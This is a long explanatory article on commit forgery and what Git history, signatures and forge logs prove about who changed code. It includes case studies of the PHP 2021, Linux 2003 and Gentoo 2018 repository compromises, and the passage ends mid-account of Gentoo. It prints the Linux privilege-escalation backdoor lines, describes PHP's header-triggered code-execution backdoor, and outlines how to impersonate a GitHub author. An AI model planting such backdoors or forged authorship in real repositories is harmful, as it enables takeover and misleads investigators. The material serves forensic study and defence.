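# Forged Commits and What Version History Can Prove About Changes to AI Safeguards

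## What does Git record about who made a change?

Git is a version control system, a program that keeps the successive states of a set of files so that people can compare them, go back to an old one or work on several versions side by side. Nearly 94% of developers in one survey used it, according to *Rethinking Trust in Forge-Based Git Security* by Yelgundhalli, Zielinski and colleagues. Each saved state is called a *commit* and carries people's names, which Git does not check. In March 2021, someone added two malicious commits to the source code of the programming language PHP under the names of two of its best-known maintainers.

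Many organisations keep settings in Git alongside their code, and an AI company can do the same with its *safety configuration*, the files and settings that determine how its safeguards behave. One such safeguard is a safety filter, which examines what users send to an AI system, or what the system produces, and blocks material in forbidden categories. Often the filter gives each text a score and blocks those that score above a fixed number, the threshold. If someone raises the threshold and the system then lets through instructions for making a weapon, the company, a regulator or a court may need to find out who raised it. If the safety configuration is in Git, the obvious place to start is the commit that changed the threshold.

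### The parts of a commit

A commit belongs to a *repository*, a collection of files together with its history. Take an invented case in which a settings file contained the line `block_above: 0.50` and now contains `block_above: 0.90`. Git would store the commit as a few lines of text, roughly like this, with the long identifiers cut short:

```
tree 7d3f0c
parent 91be42
author Ana Ruiz <ana@example.com> 1772442000 +0000
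committer Ben Okafor <ben@example.com> 1772528400 +0000

Raise blocking threshold to cut false alarms
```

The `tree` line holds the identifier of a directory listing, which holds the identifiers of every file and subdirectory in the repository at that moment. The commit doesn't record the change from 0.50 to 0.90. According to the data-model document in Git's documentation, Git works out the difference when someone asks for it, by comparing the commit with the earlier one identified on its `parent` line. A repository's first commit has no parent, and a commit that merges lines of work has two or more.

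The `author` line is meant to name whoever wrote the change, and the `committer` line whoever turned it into a commit. On a small team the two usually match. They differ when a maintainer applies a patch that somebody else sent in, or when a developer edits a file on the website of the hosting service GitHub, which lists itself as committer. Each line ends with a date, given as the number of seconds since the start of 1970, followed by an offset from universal time. Here the dates are 9 a.m. on 2 March 2026 and 9 a.m. on 3 March 2026.

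Git doesn't require proof of the names, email addresses and dates it records. According to the manual page for committing in Git, the program first checks six environment variables, which a user or a script can set before running a command. If it finds no name or address there, it uses the `user.name` and `user.email` settings, which most developers fill in once on a new computer. If those are missing too, it uses the computer's login name and mail host. Git strips angle brackets and line breaks but otherwise accepts any text, and according to the manual the name "has no effect on authentication". The dates come from the computer's clock unless the user supplies others. A person can therefore commit as Ana Ruiz on a day in 2020 by changing the name and email settings and setting one date variable.

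The commit message is also free text, including any lines at its end that look like structured data. A common example is the "Co-authored-by:" line, which gives another contributor's name and email address. *Weaponizing the Commons* (2026), a study of abuse on GitHub, documents people who add famous developers as co-authors to make a repository look trustworthy. GitHub does not notify those developers, so they may never find out.

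A commit can also contain a signature between the committer line and the message. The signer's software computes it from the rest of the commit using a private key, a secret number that only the signer should hold. The signature ties the commit to that key, but not necessarily to a particular person. Ana's commit has no signature, and Git treats it as complete without one.

The last item is the *commit hash*, the identifier people and programs use to refer to the commit. Git computes it by running the commit's full contents through a hash function, which turns input of any length into a short string of fixed length. Most repositories still use SHA-1, which produces a string of 40 hexadecimal digits. The hash covers every line inside the commit, including the signature if there is one, but is not itself one of those lines. So the creator freely chooses both names, both addresses, both dates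 and the message, while Git computes the tree identifier from the files and the commit hash from the full contents of the commit.

### What the chain of hashes protects

Because each commit contains its parent's hash, the hashes form a chain. Write H for the hash function and number three commits in a row:

- h₁ = H(tree₁, author₁, committer₁, message₁)
- h₂ = H(tree₂, h₁, author₂, committer₂, message₂)
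- h₃ = H(tree₃, h₂, author₃, committer₃, message₃)

Suppose somebody wants to replace the author of commit 2. The new name changes the input to H, so the edited commit has a different hash. Commit 3 still contains the old h₂ and therefore still points to the original. To make commit 3 point to the edited commit, the editor has to write the new hash into it, which changes h₃, and so on through every later commit to the newest one. Git's stored commits are fixed once they exist, so these edits create a second chain next to the old one.

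Anyone who recorded h₂ or h₃ before the edit can detect it by comparing that hash with the new chain. Such records are common because every developer who copies the repository receives its whole history, and many build systems record the hash of the commit they built from. Having only h₁ would not help, since commit 1 comes before the edited commit and its hash stays the same. The new chain is internally consistent, so someone who first copies the repository after the edit can't detect the change from the chain without an older hash to compare. *Git Hash Chain Malleability* (Ginesin, 2026) adds that the same signed content can have more than one valid hash, though the full original hash still identifies the original commit.

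The hash chain protects a commit from the moment it is created, but the name in it may already be false. The hash depends only on the commit's bytes, so if an intruder makes the same change to the same files, enters Ana's and Ben's names, and sets the same dates and message, the result is identical to the genuine unsigned commit, including its hash. The chain can therefore show that the author field contains the same name today as it did in March, but other evidence is needed to establish whether Ana had anything to do with the commit.

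*Claimed or Attested?* (Mockus, 2026) points out that researchers who want to know which commits belong to which developer have to start from author strings, and that those strings are claims. Unrelated people commit as "root", the standard name of a computer's administrator account, and impostors reuse well-known names and addresses.

### Branches, tags and pushes

Commit identifiers are 40 digits long and awkward to work with, so Git lets people give commits names, called *references*. A branch is a reference to the newest commit in a line of work, and it moves forward each time someone adds a commit. A tag is a reference that people normally leave in place, for instance to mark the commit from which they built version 2.1. Both are little more than a name and a hash, and anyone with the necessary rights can point either one at a different commit. Moving a reference doesn't change any commit,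 so the hashes in the chain don't show that it moved.

A commit starts on one person's computer, where it affects nobody else. It reaches the rest of the team through a *push*, which sends commits to a shared repository and updates that repository's references to include them. By default, Git rejects a push to a branch if the new commit does not descend from the one the branch already points to. A *force-push* overrides that check and can replace part of the branch's history. The replaced commits then have no reference leading to them, and Git may eventually delete them. GitHub advises anyone who loses a commit this way to ask a colleague who still has a copy.

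Pushing commits does not change them, so they do not record who pushed them. Ben can push Ana's commits, for example, and they will be identical to the ones she made. Git records changes to branches and other references in a log called the reflog, but each computer's reflog covers only its local copy of the repository, and Git does not send it to other computers. A copy of the repository therefore shows the threshold change, its stated author and its stated date, but not who put it on the branch that the company's systems use.

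A record of who pushed a change exists, if at all, on the server. Most teams rent or run a *forge*, a service such as GitHub or GitLab that hosts repositories, requires users to log in and decides which accounts may push to what. The forge can keep a *push log* of which account moved which reference and when. GitHub's activity view draws on such a log and, according to GitHub's *Using the activity view to see changes to a repository*, connects pushes, force-pushes and branch changes with authenticated users. Before GitHub introduced the view in May 2023, people had to write to customer support to see the pushes to a repository (GitHub, 2023). Yelgundhalli and colleagues point out that a compromised forge or a dishonest administrator could drop or reorder log entries, and users would have no way to check.

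### Five identities behind one change

The question "who changed the threshold?" can therefore have up to five correct answers for a single commit. Suppose Ana wrote the new value, and Ben turned her patch into a commit on GitHub's website, where GitHub signed it with its own key. An account named `release-bot` later pushed the commit to the company's production repository. That account was run by an AI coding agent, which a third colleague, Chen, had started. Everyone acted properly, but the commit names only two of them.

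| Identity | In the example | Where a record exists |
|---|---|---|
| Named author | Ana | Author field of the commit, in every copy |
| Named committer | GitHub, acting for Ben | Committer field of the commit, in every copy |
| Holder of the signing key | GitHub | The signature points to a key; the link from key to holder lies outside the commit |
| Account that pushed | `release-bot` | Push log of the forge |
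| Person or program using the account | An AI agent, on Chen's instructions | No standard record; sometimes traces in login, token or session logs |

A commit's signing key seldom identifies its author, though readers often treat the two as the same. Mockus found signatures on 17.59% of the 5.87 billion commits in World of Code, a research archive of public repositories. Many of those signatures came from a platform. GitHub automatically signs commits that users make through its website, according to its *About commit signature verification*, and one such GitHub key is associated with more than 30 million different authors in Mockus's data. Of about 62.6 million authors in the archive, 49% had no signed commits, about half had only signatures that identify a platform, and 0.74% had a key that Mockus could treat as personal.

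The account that pushed the change is better evidence, because the forge required a password, key or token before accepting the push. But the account only shows whose credentials were used, not who used them. Larger organisations can narrow this down with an audit log. GitHub's *Identifying audit log events performed by an access token* describes one that stores the type of access token behind an action and a fingerprint of that token. If the company knows that one token was kept on Chen's laptop and another in an automated job, it can use the log to work out which was used, but not whether Chen's token was used by Chen or by a thief who had copied it. Ravich and Fire (2026), in *Stylometric Defenses Against Author Impersonation in Software Repositories*, call this the identity gap: signatures and access controls establish who authorised a change, but that may not be the person who wrote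 it.

Their own remedy is to compare the style of commits. They trained a model on more than twenty years of commits to the Linux kernel, the core of the Linux operating system, to judge whether two changes come from the same author. It scored 0.93 on the standard measure for such tasks, which means that, given one pair of commits by the same person and one pair by different people, the model rates the first pair as more alike 93% of the time. That is good enough to help reviewers decide which suspicious commits to check first, but it is weak evidence of who wrote them. The evidence is even weaker for a change to a safety threshold, which may be a single digit, leaving the model little to compare beyond the commit message.

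AI coding agents have made it common for a commit's named author to differ from its real one, even without an intruder. In many set-ups, the agents commit the code they write. *Promises, Perils, and (Timely) Heuristics for Mining Coding Agent Activity* (2026) notes that they may or may not disclose this, most often through a co-author line in the commit message. *Long-horizon autoformalization of a core theorem underlying MIP* = RE* (2026) describes a project to put a proof from theoretical computer science into a form that a computer can check. Language models generated all 2,778 commits in the repository, but Git's metadata credits 2,314 of them (83.3%) to human author accounts, and only 324 of those have a line naming an agent as co-author. This was not a deliberate deception, because in the early months the agents ran on developers' own machines and used the names and addresses in those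 machines' Git settings.

Coding agents differ in how their commits identify them. Commits by OpenAI's agent Codex appear under the developer's GitHub login, and *Who Finishes the Job?* (2026) found some marker of the agent on fewer than 2% of them. GitHub's agent, Copilot, lists itself as author and the person who gave it the task as co-author. Since March 2026 its commit messages have also included a link to the session log, as GitHub's *Trace any Copilot coding agent commit to its session logs* (2026) announced. Two weeks later, GitHub's *Copilot cloud agent signs its commits* (2026) announced that the agent now signs every commit it makes. The session log is the most valuable of these records to an investigator because it can help distinguish what the person asked for from what the agent did on its own. Anyone can still type any name in the author and co-author lines, so an intruder could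 enter "Copilot" or a developer's name, such as "Ana Ruiz".

### From an email address to a profile

Most people read commits on a forge's web pages, not in the raw form shown above. These pages show the author with a picture and a link to a profile. On GitHub, both depend on the email address in the commit. GitHub's *Troubleshooting commits* explains that the site links the commit to the account that has registered that address. It also says that a mistaken link doesn't give the other person access to the repository. The link is only for display and has no connection with the login used to push the commit.

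*On the Prevalence and Usage of Commit Signing on GitHub* (Sharma and Kancherla, 2025) shows how an attacker can impersonate a victim, using a test account for each. The attacker finds the victim's email address by adding `.patch` to the URL of one of the victim's commits in any public repository. The attacker then enters the victim's name and email address in Git's settings, makes a commit and pushes it from the attacker's own account. GitHub shows the victim's profile as the author. The commit doesn't appear in either account's activity overview, so the victim has no reason to notice it.

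*GitHub Commit Autopsy* examines a real commit, with a recorded date of 9 January 2026, that appears to belong to `actions/checkout`, a repository GitHub maintains. The commit lists Guillermo Rauch, chief executive of the web company Vercel, as its author, but an impostor typed his name and email address and wrote a message in the style of a routine bug fix, complete with a reference number. The data GitHub supplies to other programs about this commit has two author entries. One repeats the typed name and address. The other gives Rauch's actual GitHub login and account number, which GitHub looked up from the email address. A person or script that reads only this second entry could easily assume that Rauch had logged in to make the commit. The commit's web address is also misleading, because GitHub stores a repository together with its forks (copies made by other users) and displays a commit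 from any of them under the original's address. Nobody had ever merged this commit into `actions/checkout`.

The page does offer a hint, because the commit lacked the "Verified" badge that GitHub puts on commits with a valid signature. But according to GitHub's *Displaying verification statuses for all of your commits*, an unsigned commit shows no status by default, so only readers who know about the badge would notice its absence. Users can turn on vigilant mode, which labels unsigned commits in their name "Unverified", including genuine ones they forgot to sign.

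The link can also go wrong in the opposite direction, so that an innocent developer's work appears under a stranger's profile. Sharma and Kancherla found that a person could add someone else's email address to a GitHub account if no other account had registered it. GitHub would then credit commits with that address to the account, even though the owner of the address had never confirmed it.

To fix this, Sharma and Kancherla propose that GitHub compare the name and address in a commit with the account that pushed it or opened the request to merge it, and show a profile only if they match or an earlier match exists. The profile shown would then depend on a login. Some honest commits would also lose their profile, for example when a maintainer merges a colleague's work on a private machine and pushes the result.

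## What happened in the PHP breach, and how was the push traced?

Web servers use PHP to build pages when visitors request them. *Hackers backdoor PHP source code after internal repo hack* (Cimpanu, 2021) reports that almost 80% of websites used it in 2021. PHP's own source code is in a repository called php-src. Until March 2021, the project kept the official copy on its own server, git.php.net, and GitHub hosted a mirror, a second copy updated to match the official one. The two malicious commits reached the official copy on 28 March. One was under the name of Rasmus Lerdorf, who created PHP, and the other was under the name of Nikita Popov, one of its leading maintainers.

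Almost all the public evidence about the pushes comes from two messages that Nikita Popov sent to the PHP developers' mailing list. He sent the first, *Changes to Git commit workflow* (2021), about five hours after a colleague removed the second commit. In it he wrote that everything pointed to a compromise of the git.php.net server. He withdrew that explanation on 6 April in the second message, which includes an excerpt from the server's logs.

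### Two commits about a typo

The first commit was titled "[skip-ci] Fix typo". The "[skip-ci]" tag makes many automated systems skip building and testing the new version. PHP.Watch's *git.php.net server compromised, move to GitHub, and delayed updates* (2021) reproduces the commit in full, with Lerdorf's name and email address in both the author and committer fields. The message ended with the line "Signed-off-by: Rasmus Lerdorf". Many projects use such lines to record that a contributor vouches for a change, but they are ordinary text, not cryptographic signatures.

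The supposed typo fix added eleven lines to the part of PHP that compresses pages before a server sends them. The new lines checked each request for a header (a labelled piece of information sent with a web request) called "User-Agentt", a misspelling of the standard "User-Agent". If the header contained the trigger word "zerodium", PHP ran the text after that word as code. Anyone who knew the trigger could have run commands on any website that used this version of PHP and its page compression.

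The inserted code also contained a note that it had been sold in mid-2017 to Zerodium, a company that bought undisclosed software flaws. Zerodium's chief executive, Chaouki Bekrar, denied any involvement and called the attackers trolls, according to a CSO article republished by The Cyber Post. The attacker chose the text of the note, just as they chose the name in the author field, and nobody has produced evidence that the sale took place.

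Other developers caught the change by reading it. According to the same article, one contributor pointed out a typo in the new code about two hours after the push. WeLiveSecurity credits Markus Staab, Michael Voříšek and Jake Birchall with noticing the change. Voříšek asked what it was for, and Birchall answered that it executed PHP code from a request header. Popov then reverted the commit by adding a new one that undid its changes, so the malicious commit stayed in the history.

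About seven hours later, the same code appeared again, this time under Popov's name. The commit's title, which Devtalk reproduces, was `Revert "Revert "[skip-ci] Fix typo""`. At that time, Git generated titles of this form when someone reverted a revert, so it looked as though Popov had changed his mind. Another maintainer, Levi Morrison, removed the code again.

Both commits went to the development branch for PHP 8.1, which the project did not plan to release until November, so no released version contained the backdoor. The attacker had made it easy to find by using an unusual tag, a conspicuous trigger word and the names of two of the most closely watched people in the project. According to the CSO article, the attacker could have used the same access to add a subtler flaw under a less prominent developer's name. The quick discovery is therefore a poor guide to how fast reviewers would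 find a change that someone had tried to hide.

### The timeline in UTC

The records use three time zones. The server's log used a time zone seven hours behind Coordinated Universal Time (UTC), so the first push appears there on the evening of 27 March. Popov's revert is recorded in a time zone two hours ahead of UTC, and Morrison's in one six hours behind. The table gives all times in UTC, so every event falls on 28 March.

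| Time (UTC) | Event | Where the time comes from |
|---|---|---|
| 02:19:23 and 02:19:28 | The server refuses two requests under a name beginning `rasmus@` | Web server log |
| 03:56:51 | The server accepts a request under the name `rasmus` | Web server log |
| 03:57:07 | Date written in the first malicious commit | Commit |
| 03:58:13 | The first malicious push arrives | Web server log |
| 09:16:39 | Popov reverts the first commit | Commit |
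| 16:09:15 to 16:09:53 | The server refuses six requests under `nikita.ppv`, `nikitappv` and `nikita` | Web server log |
| 16:11:31 | The server refuses two requests under `nikic` | Web server log |
| 16:13:28 | The server accepts a request under `nikic` | Web server log |
| 16:13:39 | The second malicious push arrives | Web server log |
| 17:53:17 | Morrison reverts the second commit | Commit |
| 22:52:24 | Popov sends his first message | Email |

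Whoever made the commits in the table could set their dates, but the times in the web server's log come from the server's own clock, which someone pushing from outside cannot set.

The attacker seems not to have changed the date of the first malicious commit. It falls 16 seconds after the server first accepted a request under the name `rasmus` and 66 seconds before the push. This timing is a reason to believe the date, but only because the server log recorded the request and the push. The commit also gives a time zone two hours ahead of UTC, which matches summer time in central Europe. This is not evidence that the attacker was in Europe, because Git stores the time zone in the same unverified field as the date.

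The first malicious commit stayed in place for 5 hours and 18 minutes, from 03:58:13 to 09:16:39. The second stayed for 1 hour and 40 minutes, from 16:13:39 to 17:53:17. In total, the backdoor was in the development branch for just under seven hours over a period of nearly fourteen hours. These durations are approximate because each starts at a server time and ends at the date in a maintainer's commit, and Popov and Morrison may have pushed their reverts slightly later than they made them.

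Contemporary reports give other figures for how long the commits stayed in place. iTnews' *PHP suffers supply-chain attack* cites Popov as saying they were removed after about two hours, which fits only the second commit. PHP.Watch's first article says the backdoor was gone within 12 hours, which is about two hours too short counting from the first push to the last revert.

PHP.Watch's *Update to recent git.php.net incident* (2021), otherwise the most detailed account outside the mailing list, has a more confusing error in its timeline. It gives the same server time for both malicious pushes, 20:58:13 on 27 March in the log's time zone. If that were right, the second push would have undone Popov's revert more than five hours before he made it. Popov's log excerpt gives the correct time for the second push, 09:13:39 on 28 March in the same time zone, or 16:13:39 UTC. PHP.Watch also gives the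 malicious commit that Morrison reverted the date of the revert itself, almost certainly a copying error.

### From a name to an account

When Popov saw the first malicious commit, he assumed someone had taken over Lerdorf's account, so he reverted the change and revoked Lerdorf's commit access. He later told the PHP list that, in hindsight, this "didn't really make sense". Any account with write access to php-src could have pushed a commit under Lerdorf's name, and Popov had no evidence at the time of which account had.

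Even an expert can easily make this mistake. Popov knew that Git does not check author names, but he had to act quickly, and Lerdorf's was the only name he had. Revoking Lerdorf's account would have been a simple precaution if the attacker had used it. If the attacker had used another account, revoking Lerdorf's would have locked out an innocent colleague and left the attacker's access intact.

The logs later showed that the push had gone through an account called `rasmus`, as Popov had guessed, but he had based his guess on a field that could not support it. The revocation did not end the attack, because the attacker returned that afternoon with a different account. The published excerpt shows no further requests under `rasmus`, but it is unclear from the excerpt whether the revocation blocked that account or the attacker chose to impersonate the person who had removed the code.

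### From a missing log entry to a compromised server

The second malicious commit carried Popov's own name, and he knew he had not made it. He then looked for the account that had pushed it. Developers normally pushed to git.php.net over SSH, a protocol for encrypted connections to another computer, and proved their identity with a cryptographic key. The program gitolite managed these connections, controlled who could write to each repository and logged pushes.

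Popov searched that log for both malicious commits and found neither. It had entries for all the commits around them, so it had been working normally. He correctly concluded that the two commits had bypassed gitolite. He and his colleagues then took this to mean that an intruder had probably broken into the server itself, since someone in control of the machine could write to the repository directly.

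This step depended on the unchecked assumption that gitolite handled every push from outside. If the server accepted pushes by another route, those pushes would also be missing from gitolite's log. The missing entries ruled out an ordinary SSH push, but they were as consistent with a push by another route as with a break-in.

The distinction matters because an intruder who controls a server can change any repository on it, replace the programs that check users' rights, and alter or delete the logs, while one who has only a developer's password is limited to what that developer's account allows. After a server break-in, the maintainers would have had to doubt everything on the machine, including the records they were using to investigate.

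PHP.Watch reported that its staff and several PHP maintainers had their own copies of php-src, and that a comparison showed no earlier commits had been rewritten. This check did not depend on the server, because the chain of commit hashes lets anyone with an older copy detect such rewriting. It could not rule out malicious code in the earlier commits, however. An attacker could have used the same access before 28 March to add a less obvious backdoor in a new commit, which those copies would have received like any other. The project therefore reviewed the code itself and delayed PHP 8.0.4 and PHP 7.4.17 by two weeks.

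### The route nobody had checked

git.php.net did have another route. In the update of 6 April Popov explained that the server deliberately accepted pushes over HTTPS, the encrypted protocol that web browsers use, as well as over SSH. He had not known this. Pushes over HTTPS went to Apache, an ordinary web server program, which asked for a username and password and checked them against a user database on another machine, master.php.net. Apache then handed the push to Git, and gitolite played no part.

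Popov found the pushes in Apache's own access log. Each line of the excerpt has a username, a time, the request and a status code. Lines normally start with the address the request came from, but Popov removed it before publication. A 401 code means the server refused the request because it lacked valid login details, and 200 means the request succeeded.

A push over HTTPS takes two steps. The user's Git program first requests a list of the commits that the server's branches and tags point to, and marks the request as part of a push. If the server accepts, the program sends the new commits with a request to move the branch. In the excerpt, both steps succeed for `rasmus` at 03:56:51 and 03:58:13, and for `nikic`, Popov's username, at 16:13:28 and 16:13:39. The other ten of the fourteen lines record refused requests.

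These lines do not contain the hashes of the commits the server received, so Popov matched them to the malicious commits by repository, time and username. The match is still strong, because the excerpt has only two completed pushes, the first arrived about a minute after the date in the first malicious commit, and the gitolite log had already ruled out the usual route. On this basis Popov stated that the attacker had used HTTPS and passwords, and that the team no longer believed anyone had compromised git.php.net. Like any conclusion drawn from server logs, this one assumes that nobody had tampered with the logs.

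The account `rasmus` pushed the commit forged in Lerdorf's name, and the account `nikic` pushed the one forged in Popov's. An investigator with only the commits and the successful log entries would have seen the author, committer and pushing account all match, and would have blamed the wrong two people. Sharma and Kancherla propose showing a developer's profile only where a commit matches the account that pushed it, but this would not have exposed the forgery either.

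The agreement between the login account and the name on the commit adds less evidence than it seems to, because the attacker controlled both. Someone who can log in as Lerdorf can also type his name into a commit, and has good reason to, since a mismatch might attract attention. The log showed that whoever pushed the commits could pass the server's password check for two accounts, but not who that person was.

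We can learn more about the attacker from the failed requests. Before finding `nikic`, the attacker tried `nikita.ppv`, `nikitappv` and `nikita`. The first is the part before the "@" in the Gmail address Popov used on the public mailing list. Popov would hardly have needed to guess his own username, so these attempts suggest that someone else made them, working from public information. An insider could stage such guesses to look like an outsider, but there is no sign of that here.

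### How did the attacker get in?

Popov suggested that the passwords may have come from a leak of the master.php.net user database, though he had no specific evidence of one. He noted that the attacker guessed only a few usernames and got in once the name was right, as one would expect from someone who already had the passwords. The machine was also running very old code on an old operating system and PHP version, and he wrote that a vulnerability there would not be very surprising.

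The way the database stored passwords would have made a leak especially damaging. The HTTPS route used a method called Digest authentication, in which a server in the standard set-up stores this value for each user:

stored value = MD5(username : realm : password)

MD5 is an old and very fast hash function, and the realm is a fixed label for the service. At login, the server sends a random number, and the user's program answers with a hash computed from the stored value, the random number and details of the request. A thief who copies the stored value can therefore log in without learning the password. The thief can also try to find the password by hashing billions of guesses until one matches the stored value.

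Popov pointed out that the guessed usernames are evidence against a leak. A stolen user database would normally include the usernames, so the thief would have had no reason to try three wrong ones. The log also shows something Popov did not discuss, which is that the server refused two requests under the correct name `nikic` at 16:11:31 and accepted one about two minutes later. The excerpt doesn't show why the earlier requests failed. The attacker may have had technical trouble with the login, or may have tried more than one password, which would be less likely if they had the right one from the start.

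Passwords stolen from an unrelated website would explain the guesses better. Stolen passwords are usually listed with email addresses, and the first usernames the attacker tried for both men look like email addresses or parts of them. But Lerdorf and Popov would each have had to use the same password on another site, and nobody has published evidence of that either.

PHP.Watch's update reports that Popov identified the outdated PHP version and HTTPS configuration of master.php.net as the root cause, but he had only called a vulnerability there unsurprising. The headline of Paganini (2021), *User database was also hacked in the recent hack of PHP*, states the possible leak as fact, although the article's opening says only that attackers may have compromised the database.

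PHP has published no official findings since Popov's update of 6 April. It has not said who made the pushes, how that person obtained the login details or whether the addresses in the log helped identify anyone. The motive is also unclear. Ilkka Turunen of the software company Sonatype told CSO that the attack looked like an attempt to send a message about PHP's outdated infrastructure, but he was an outsider judging by how little the attacker had done to hide the code.

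### What PHP changed

The project decided to leave its own server before it knew how the attacker had got in. In his first message, Popov announced that the copies on GitHub, until then mirrors, would become the official repositories. Developers had previously received write access through karma, PHP's own permission scheme. They now had to join the project's GitHub organisation, which required two-factor authentication (a second proof of identity, such as a code from a phone, in addition to a password).

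The team made this decision because it suspected that the server had been compromised, but there were other reasons for it. Popov later explained that keeping git.php.net would have meant finding the cause of the breach and building a new server, while most repositories were already copied to GitHub, where much of the work took place. Two-factor authentication also turned out to protect against the actual method of attack, because a stolen password alone is not enough to get into an account that uses it. A subscriber to the list added that GitHub would stop accepting passwords for pushes on 13 August 2021.

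In April 2021, PHP reset every php.net password and moved master.php.net to a new machine with current software, under the name main.php.net. The new system stores passwords with bcrypt, a deliberately slow hash function, so guessing passwords from a stolen database takes far longer. Its developers also began rewriting database queries to prevent attackers from inserting their own commands. PHP made both git.php.net and its older Subversion server read-only. This ended pushes to both servers, so PHP no longer had to store passwords in the format that Digest authentication requires.

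In reply to Popov's first message, Max Semenik asked whether the project should go further and forbid direct pushes, so that every change would first go through a pull request, a proposal that others can review before it enters the branch. George Peter Banyard replied that this was excessive for trivial changes, such as fixing a typo in a comment, and preferred to require signatures on direct pushes. The attacker had relied on this tolerance for trivial changes by calling the first malicious commit a typo fix. Derick Rethans objected that separate pull requests would slow developers down, because PHP maintains several versions at once and they carry each fix from the oldest version up to the newest.

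Lerdorf thought the project could require signatures for php-src, and another developer wrote a guide to setting them up. But three years later, Rethans (2024) was still asking in *Requiring GPG Commit Signing* whether to require signing.

Another participant recalled that pushes to the repository for PHP's website used to go straight to the live site, and asked someone to check whether they still did. Reviewing commits after they were pushed had been enough to protect PHP's users because the next release from that branch was still months away. It would protect users much less well if a repository's contents took effect immediately, whether they were web pages or an AI system's safety configuration.

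### The withdrawn explanation in later accounts

Some publications corrected their reports. PHP.Watch marked its first article as outdated and linked to the new one. On 8 April, Vice added a note to *Hackers Tried To Backdoor Code Used by 80% of All Websites* quoting Popov as saying he no longer believed the server had been compromised, but left the original story below it. CPO Magazine's *PHP Team Averted a Supply Chain Attack*, published a day later, still reported that attackers had compromised the server. It also dated the attack to May instead of March, an error that also appears in the iTnews article.

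The old explanation has lasted longest in reference works, where people are most likely to look for an established account. The Cloud Native Computing Foundation, an industry body for cloud software, keeps a catalogue of attacks on the software supply chain, the people and systems through which code reaches its users. Its entry on the breach, *Compromise of PHP's development team self-hosted Git server*, describes the means of access to the server as still unknown and cites only Popov's first message for the incident. Readers who follow that citation will find a genuine statement from Popov on the official mailing list, with no sign that he later withdrew it.

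SLSA, a widely used set of security standards for the software supply chain, uses PHP as its example of an attack on a source code system. SLSA's *Supply chain threats* says that the attacker compromised PHP's self-hosted Git server, and that a better-protected system would have been a much harder target. SLSA's *The Supply Chain Problem*, a draft that will follow version 1.2 of the standard, keeps the same wording. The attacker gained write access to a repository on that server through a password login that was working as designed and that Popov, who led the investigation, did not know existed. SLSA's wording is defensible in a loose sense because this access was unauthorised, but a reader would probably wrongly conclude that PHP needed to secure the machine against intruders.

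Research papers also disagree about how the attacker got in. *Not In My Git Yard* (2026), a study of how to detect backdoors in open-source projects, reports a breach of the PHP Git server, though it also uses the incident to illustrate attacks through malicious commits, including pushes from compromised maintainer accounts. It wrongly places the backdoor in PHP's bundled web server. The attacker put it in the compression code. Ravich and Fire, who use the two commits to test their method for detecting impersonation, attribute the pushes to compromised credentials, in line with Popov's update. The two are the only malicious commits among the 26,680 in their test set.

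## Which other repository compromises misled people about who did what?

In the PHP breach, the attacker put two developers' names on the commits and logged in as those same developers, so the commits and the server log both pointed to innocent people. Other attackers have left records that contradict each other or a second copy of the code, and investigators have used those contradictions to work out what happened. Four attacks show how much it matters which record is false. They hit the Linux kernel in 2003, the Linux distribution Gentoo in 2018, the compression software XZ Utils in 2024 and an automation component called tj-actions/changed-files in 2025.

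### False revisions in a copy of Linux

In 2003 the Linux kernel's main repository was in BitKeeper, a version control system made by BitMover. Some developers disliked BitKeeper, so BitMover also published a copy of the code in CVS, an older system. CVS numbers the versions of each file separately and does not link them by hashes, so someone who can write to the server's files can add versions without causing a hash mismatch.

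On 5 November BitMover's Larry McVoy told the kernel mailing list that somebody had changed the CVS copy directly. *BK2CVS problem* (McVoy, 2003) lists three extra revisions of `kernel/exit.c`, all dated 4 November and under the author name "davem", which belonged to the kernel developer David Miller. The first added two lines and had an empty message. The second removed 58 lines nineteen minutes later, and the third put 58 lines back two minutes after that, with the message "Oops, I worked on the the wrong file, fixed again." Anyone who read only the newest entry would have seen what looked like a colleague correcting a mistake. Miller denied making any of the changes.

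The two added lines were in a function that programs use to wait for other programs to finish:

```
if ((options == (__WCLONE|__WALL)) && (current->uid = 0))
        retval = -EINVAL;
```

They look like a check that rejects an unusual combination of options. But in the language C, `==` compares two values and `=` assigns one, so the second half of the condition sets the user's number to 0, the administrator's number, instead of checking whether it is already 0. Any program that called the function with those two options would have gained full control of the machine.

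BitMover found the change because it did not trust its own public server. Its software exported the BitKeeper repository to CVS on an internal machine and copied the updated files to the public server. Every night, it compared the checksums of the internal and public files, which are short values derived from a file's contents, and sent an email if any differed. On 5 November, the public copy of `exit.c` did not match the internal one.

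McVoy then noticed that the three revisions lacked the marker "(Logical change X.YZ)", which the export program added to every message to show which BitKeeper change a revision came from. Freedom to Tinker's *The Linux Backdoor Attempt of 2003* (2013), a widely read retelling, reverses the order. In it, McVoy first noticed a change without a pointer to a record of approval, and only further investigation showed that the change was missing from BitKeeper. The order matters because the marker was ordinary text. A more careful intruder could have typed a plausible one, but could not have made the altered file match the original.

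The comparison also caught the change before anyone understood the code. In his first message, McVoy called the incident "not a big deal" and did not mention a backdoor. Another developer asked to see the lines. Twenty-eight minutes after McVoy posted them, Andries Brouwer pointed out that they would help someone trying to gain administrator access, which McVoy admitted he had missed.

He said less than 24 hours passed between the change and the repair. This is hard to check because the log entries have no time zone. His first message came about 20 hours after the earliest false revision if the entries are in Pacific time, but more than 28 hours after it if they are in UTC, which CVS normally used.

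Linus Torvalds, who created Linux and decides what goes into it, said the lines could not have reached an official release from the CVS copy. Changes reached him by email or through BitKeeper, and the people who merged through BitKeeper did not use CVS. McVoy was less sure, because a CVS user might have unknowingly sent in a patch that included the lines. Torvalds also said he would have noticed a similar change to the public BitKeeper repository at once, because his next push to it would have failed. Git also rejects such a push by default.

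The comparison showed that the entries under Miller's name had not come from the main repository, but it could not show who had written them. McVoy thought someone had either edited the file on the server or got in through the CVS service for remote users. The discussion on the list ended without a suspect.

### A takeover of Gentoo's GitHub organisation

Gentoo's developers keep their main repositories on their own servers and copy them to GitHub, where outside contributors propose changes. On 28 June 2018, someone took over an administrator's account in Gentoo's GitHub organisation. According to Gentoo's *Project:Infrastructure/Incident reports/2018-06-28 Github* (2018), the administrator seems to have used a scheme for choosing passwords, so one leaked password made the others easy to guess. The attacker entered one wrong password at 20:19 UTC and logged in within the same minute.

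At 20:25 they created a second administrator account and began removing Gentoo's developers. From 20:34 they pushed commits to the main package repository, `gentoo/gentoo`. The first added a file with racist text. Later ones changed the scripts that install Gentoo's software, adding a command to delete all of a computer's files. Technical safeguards made it unlikely that users would run the command.

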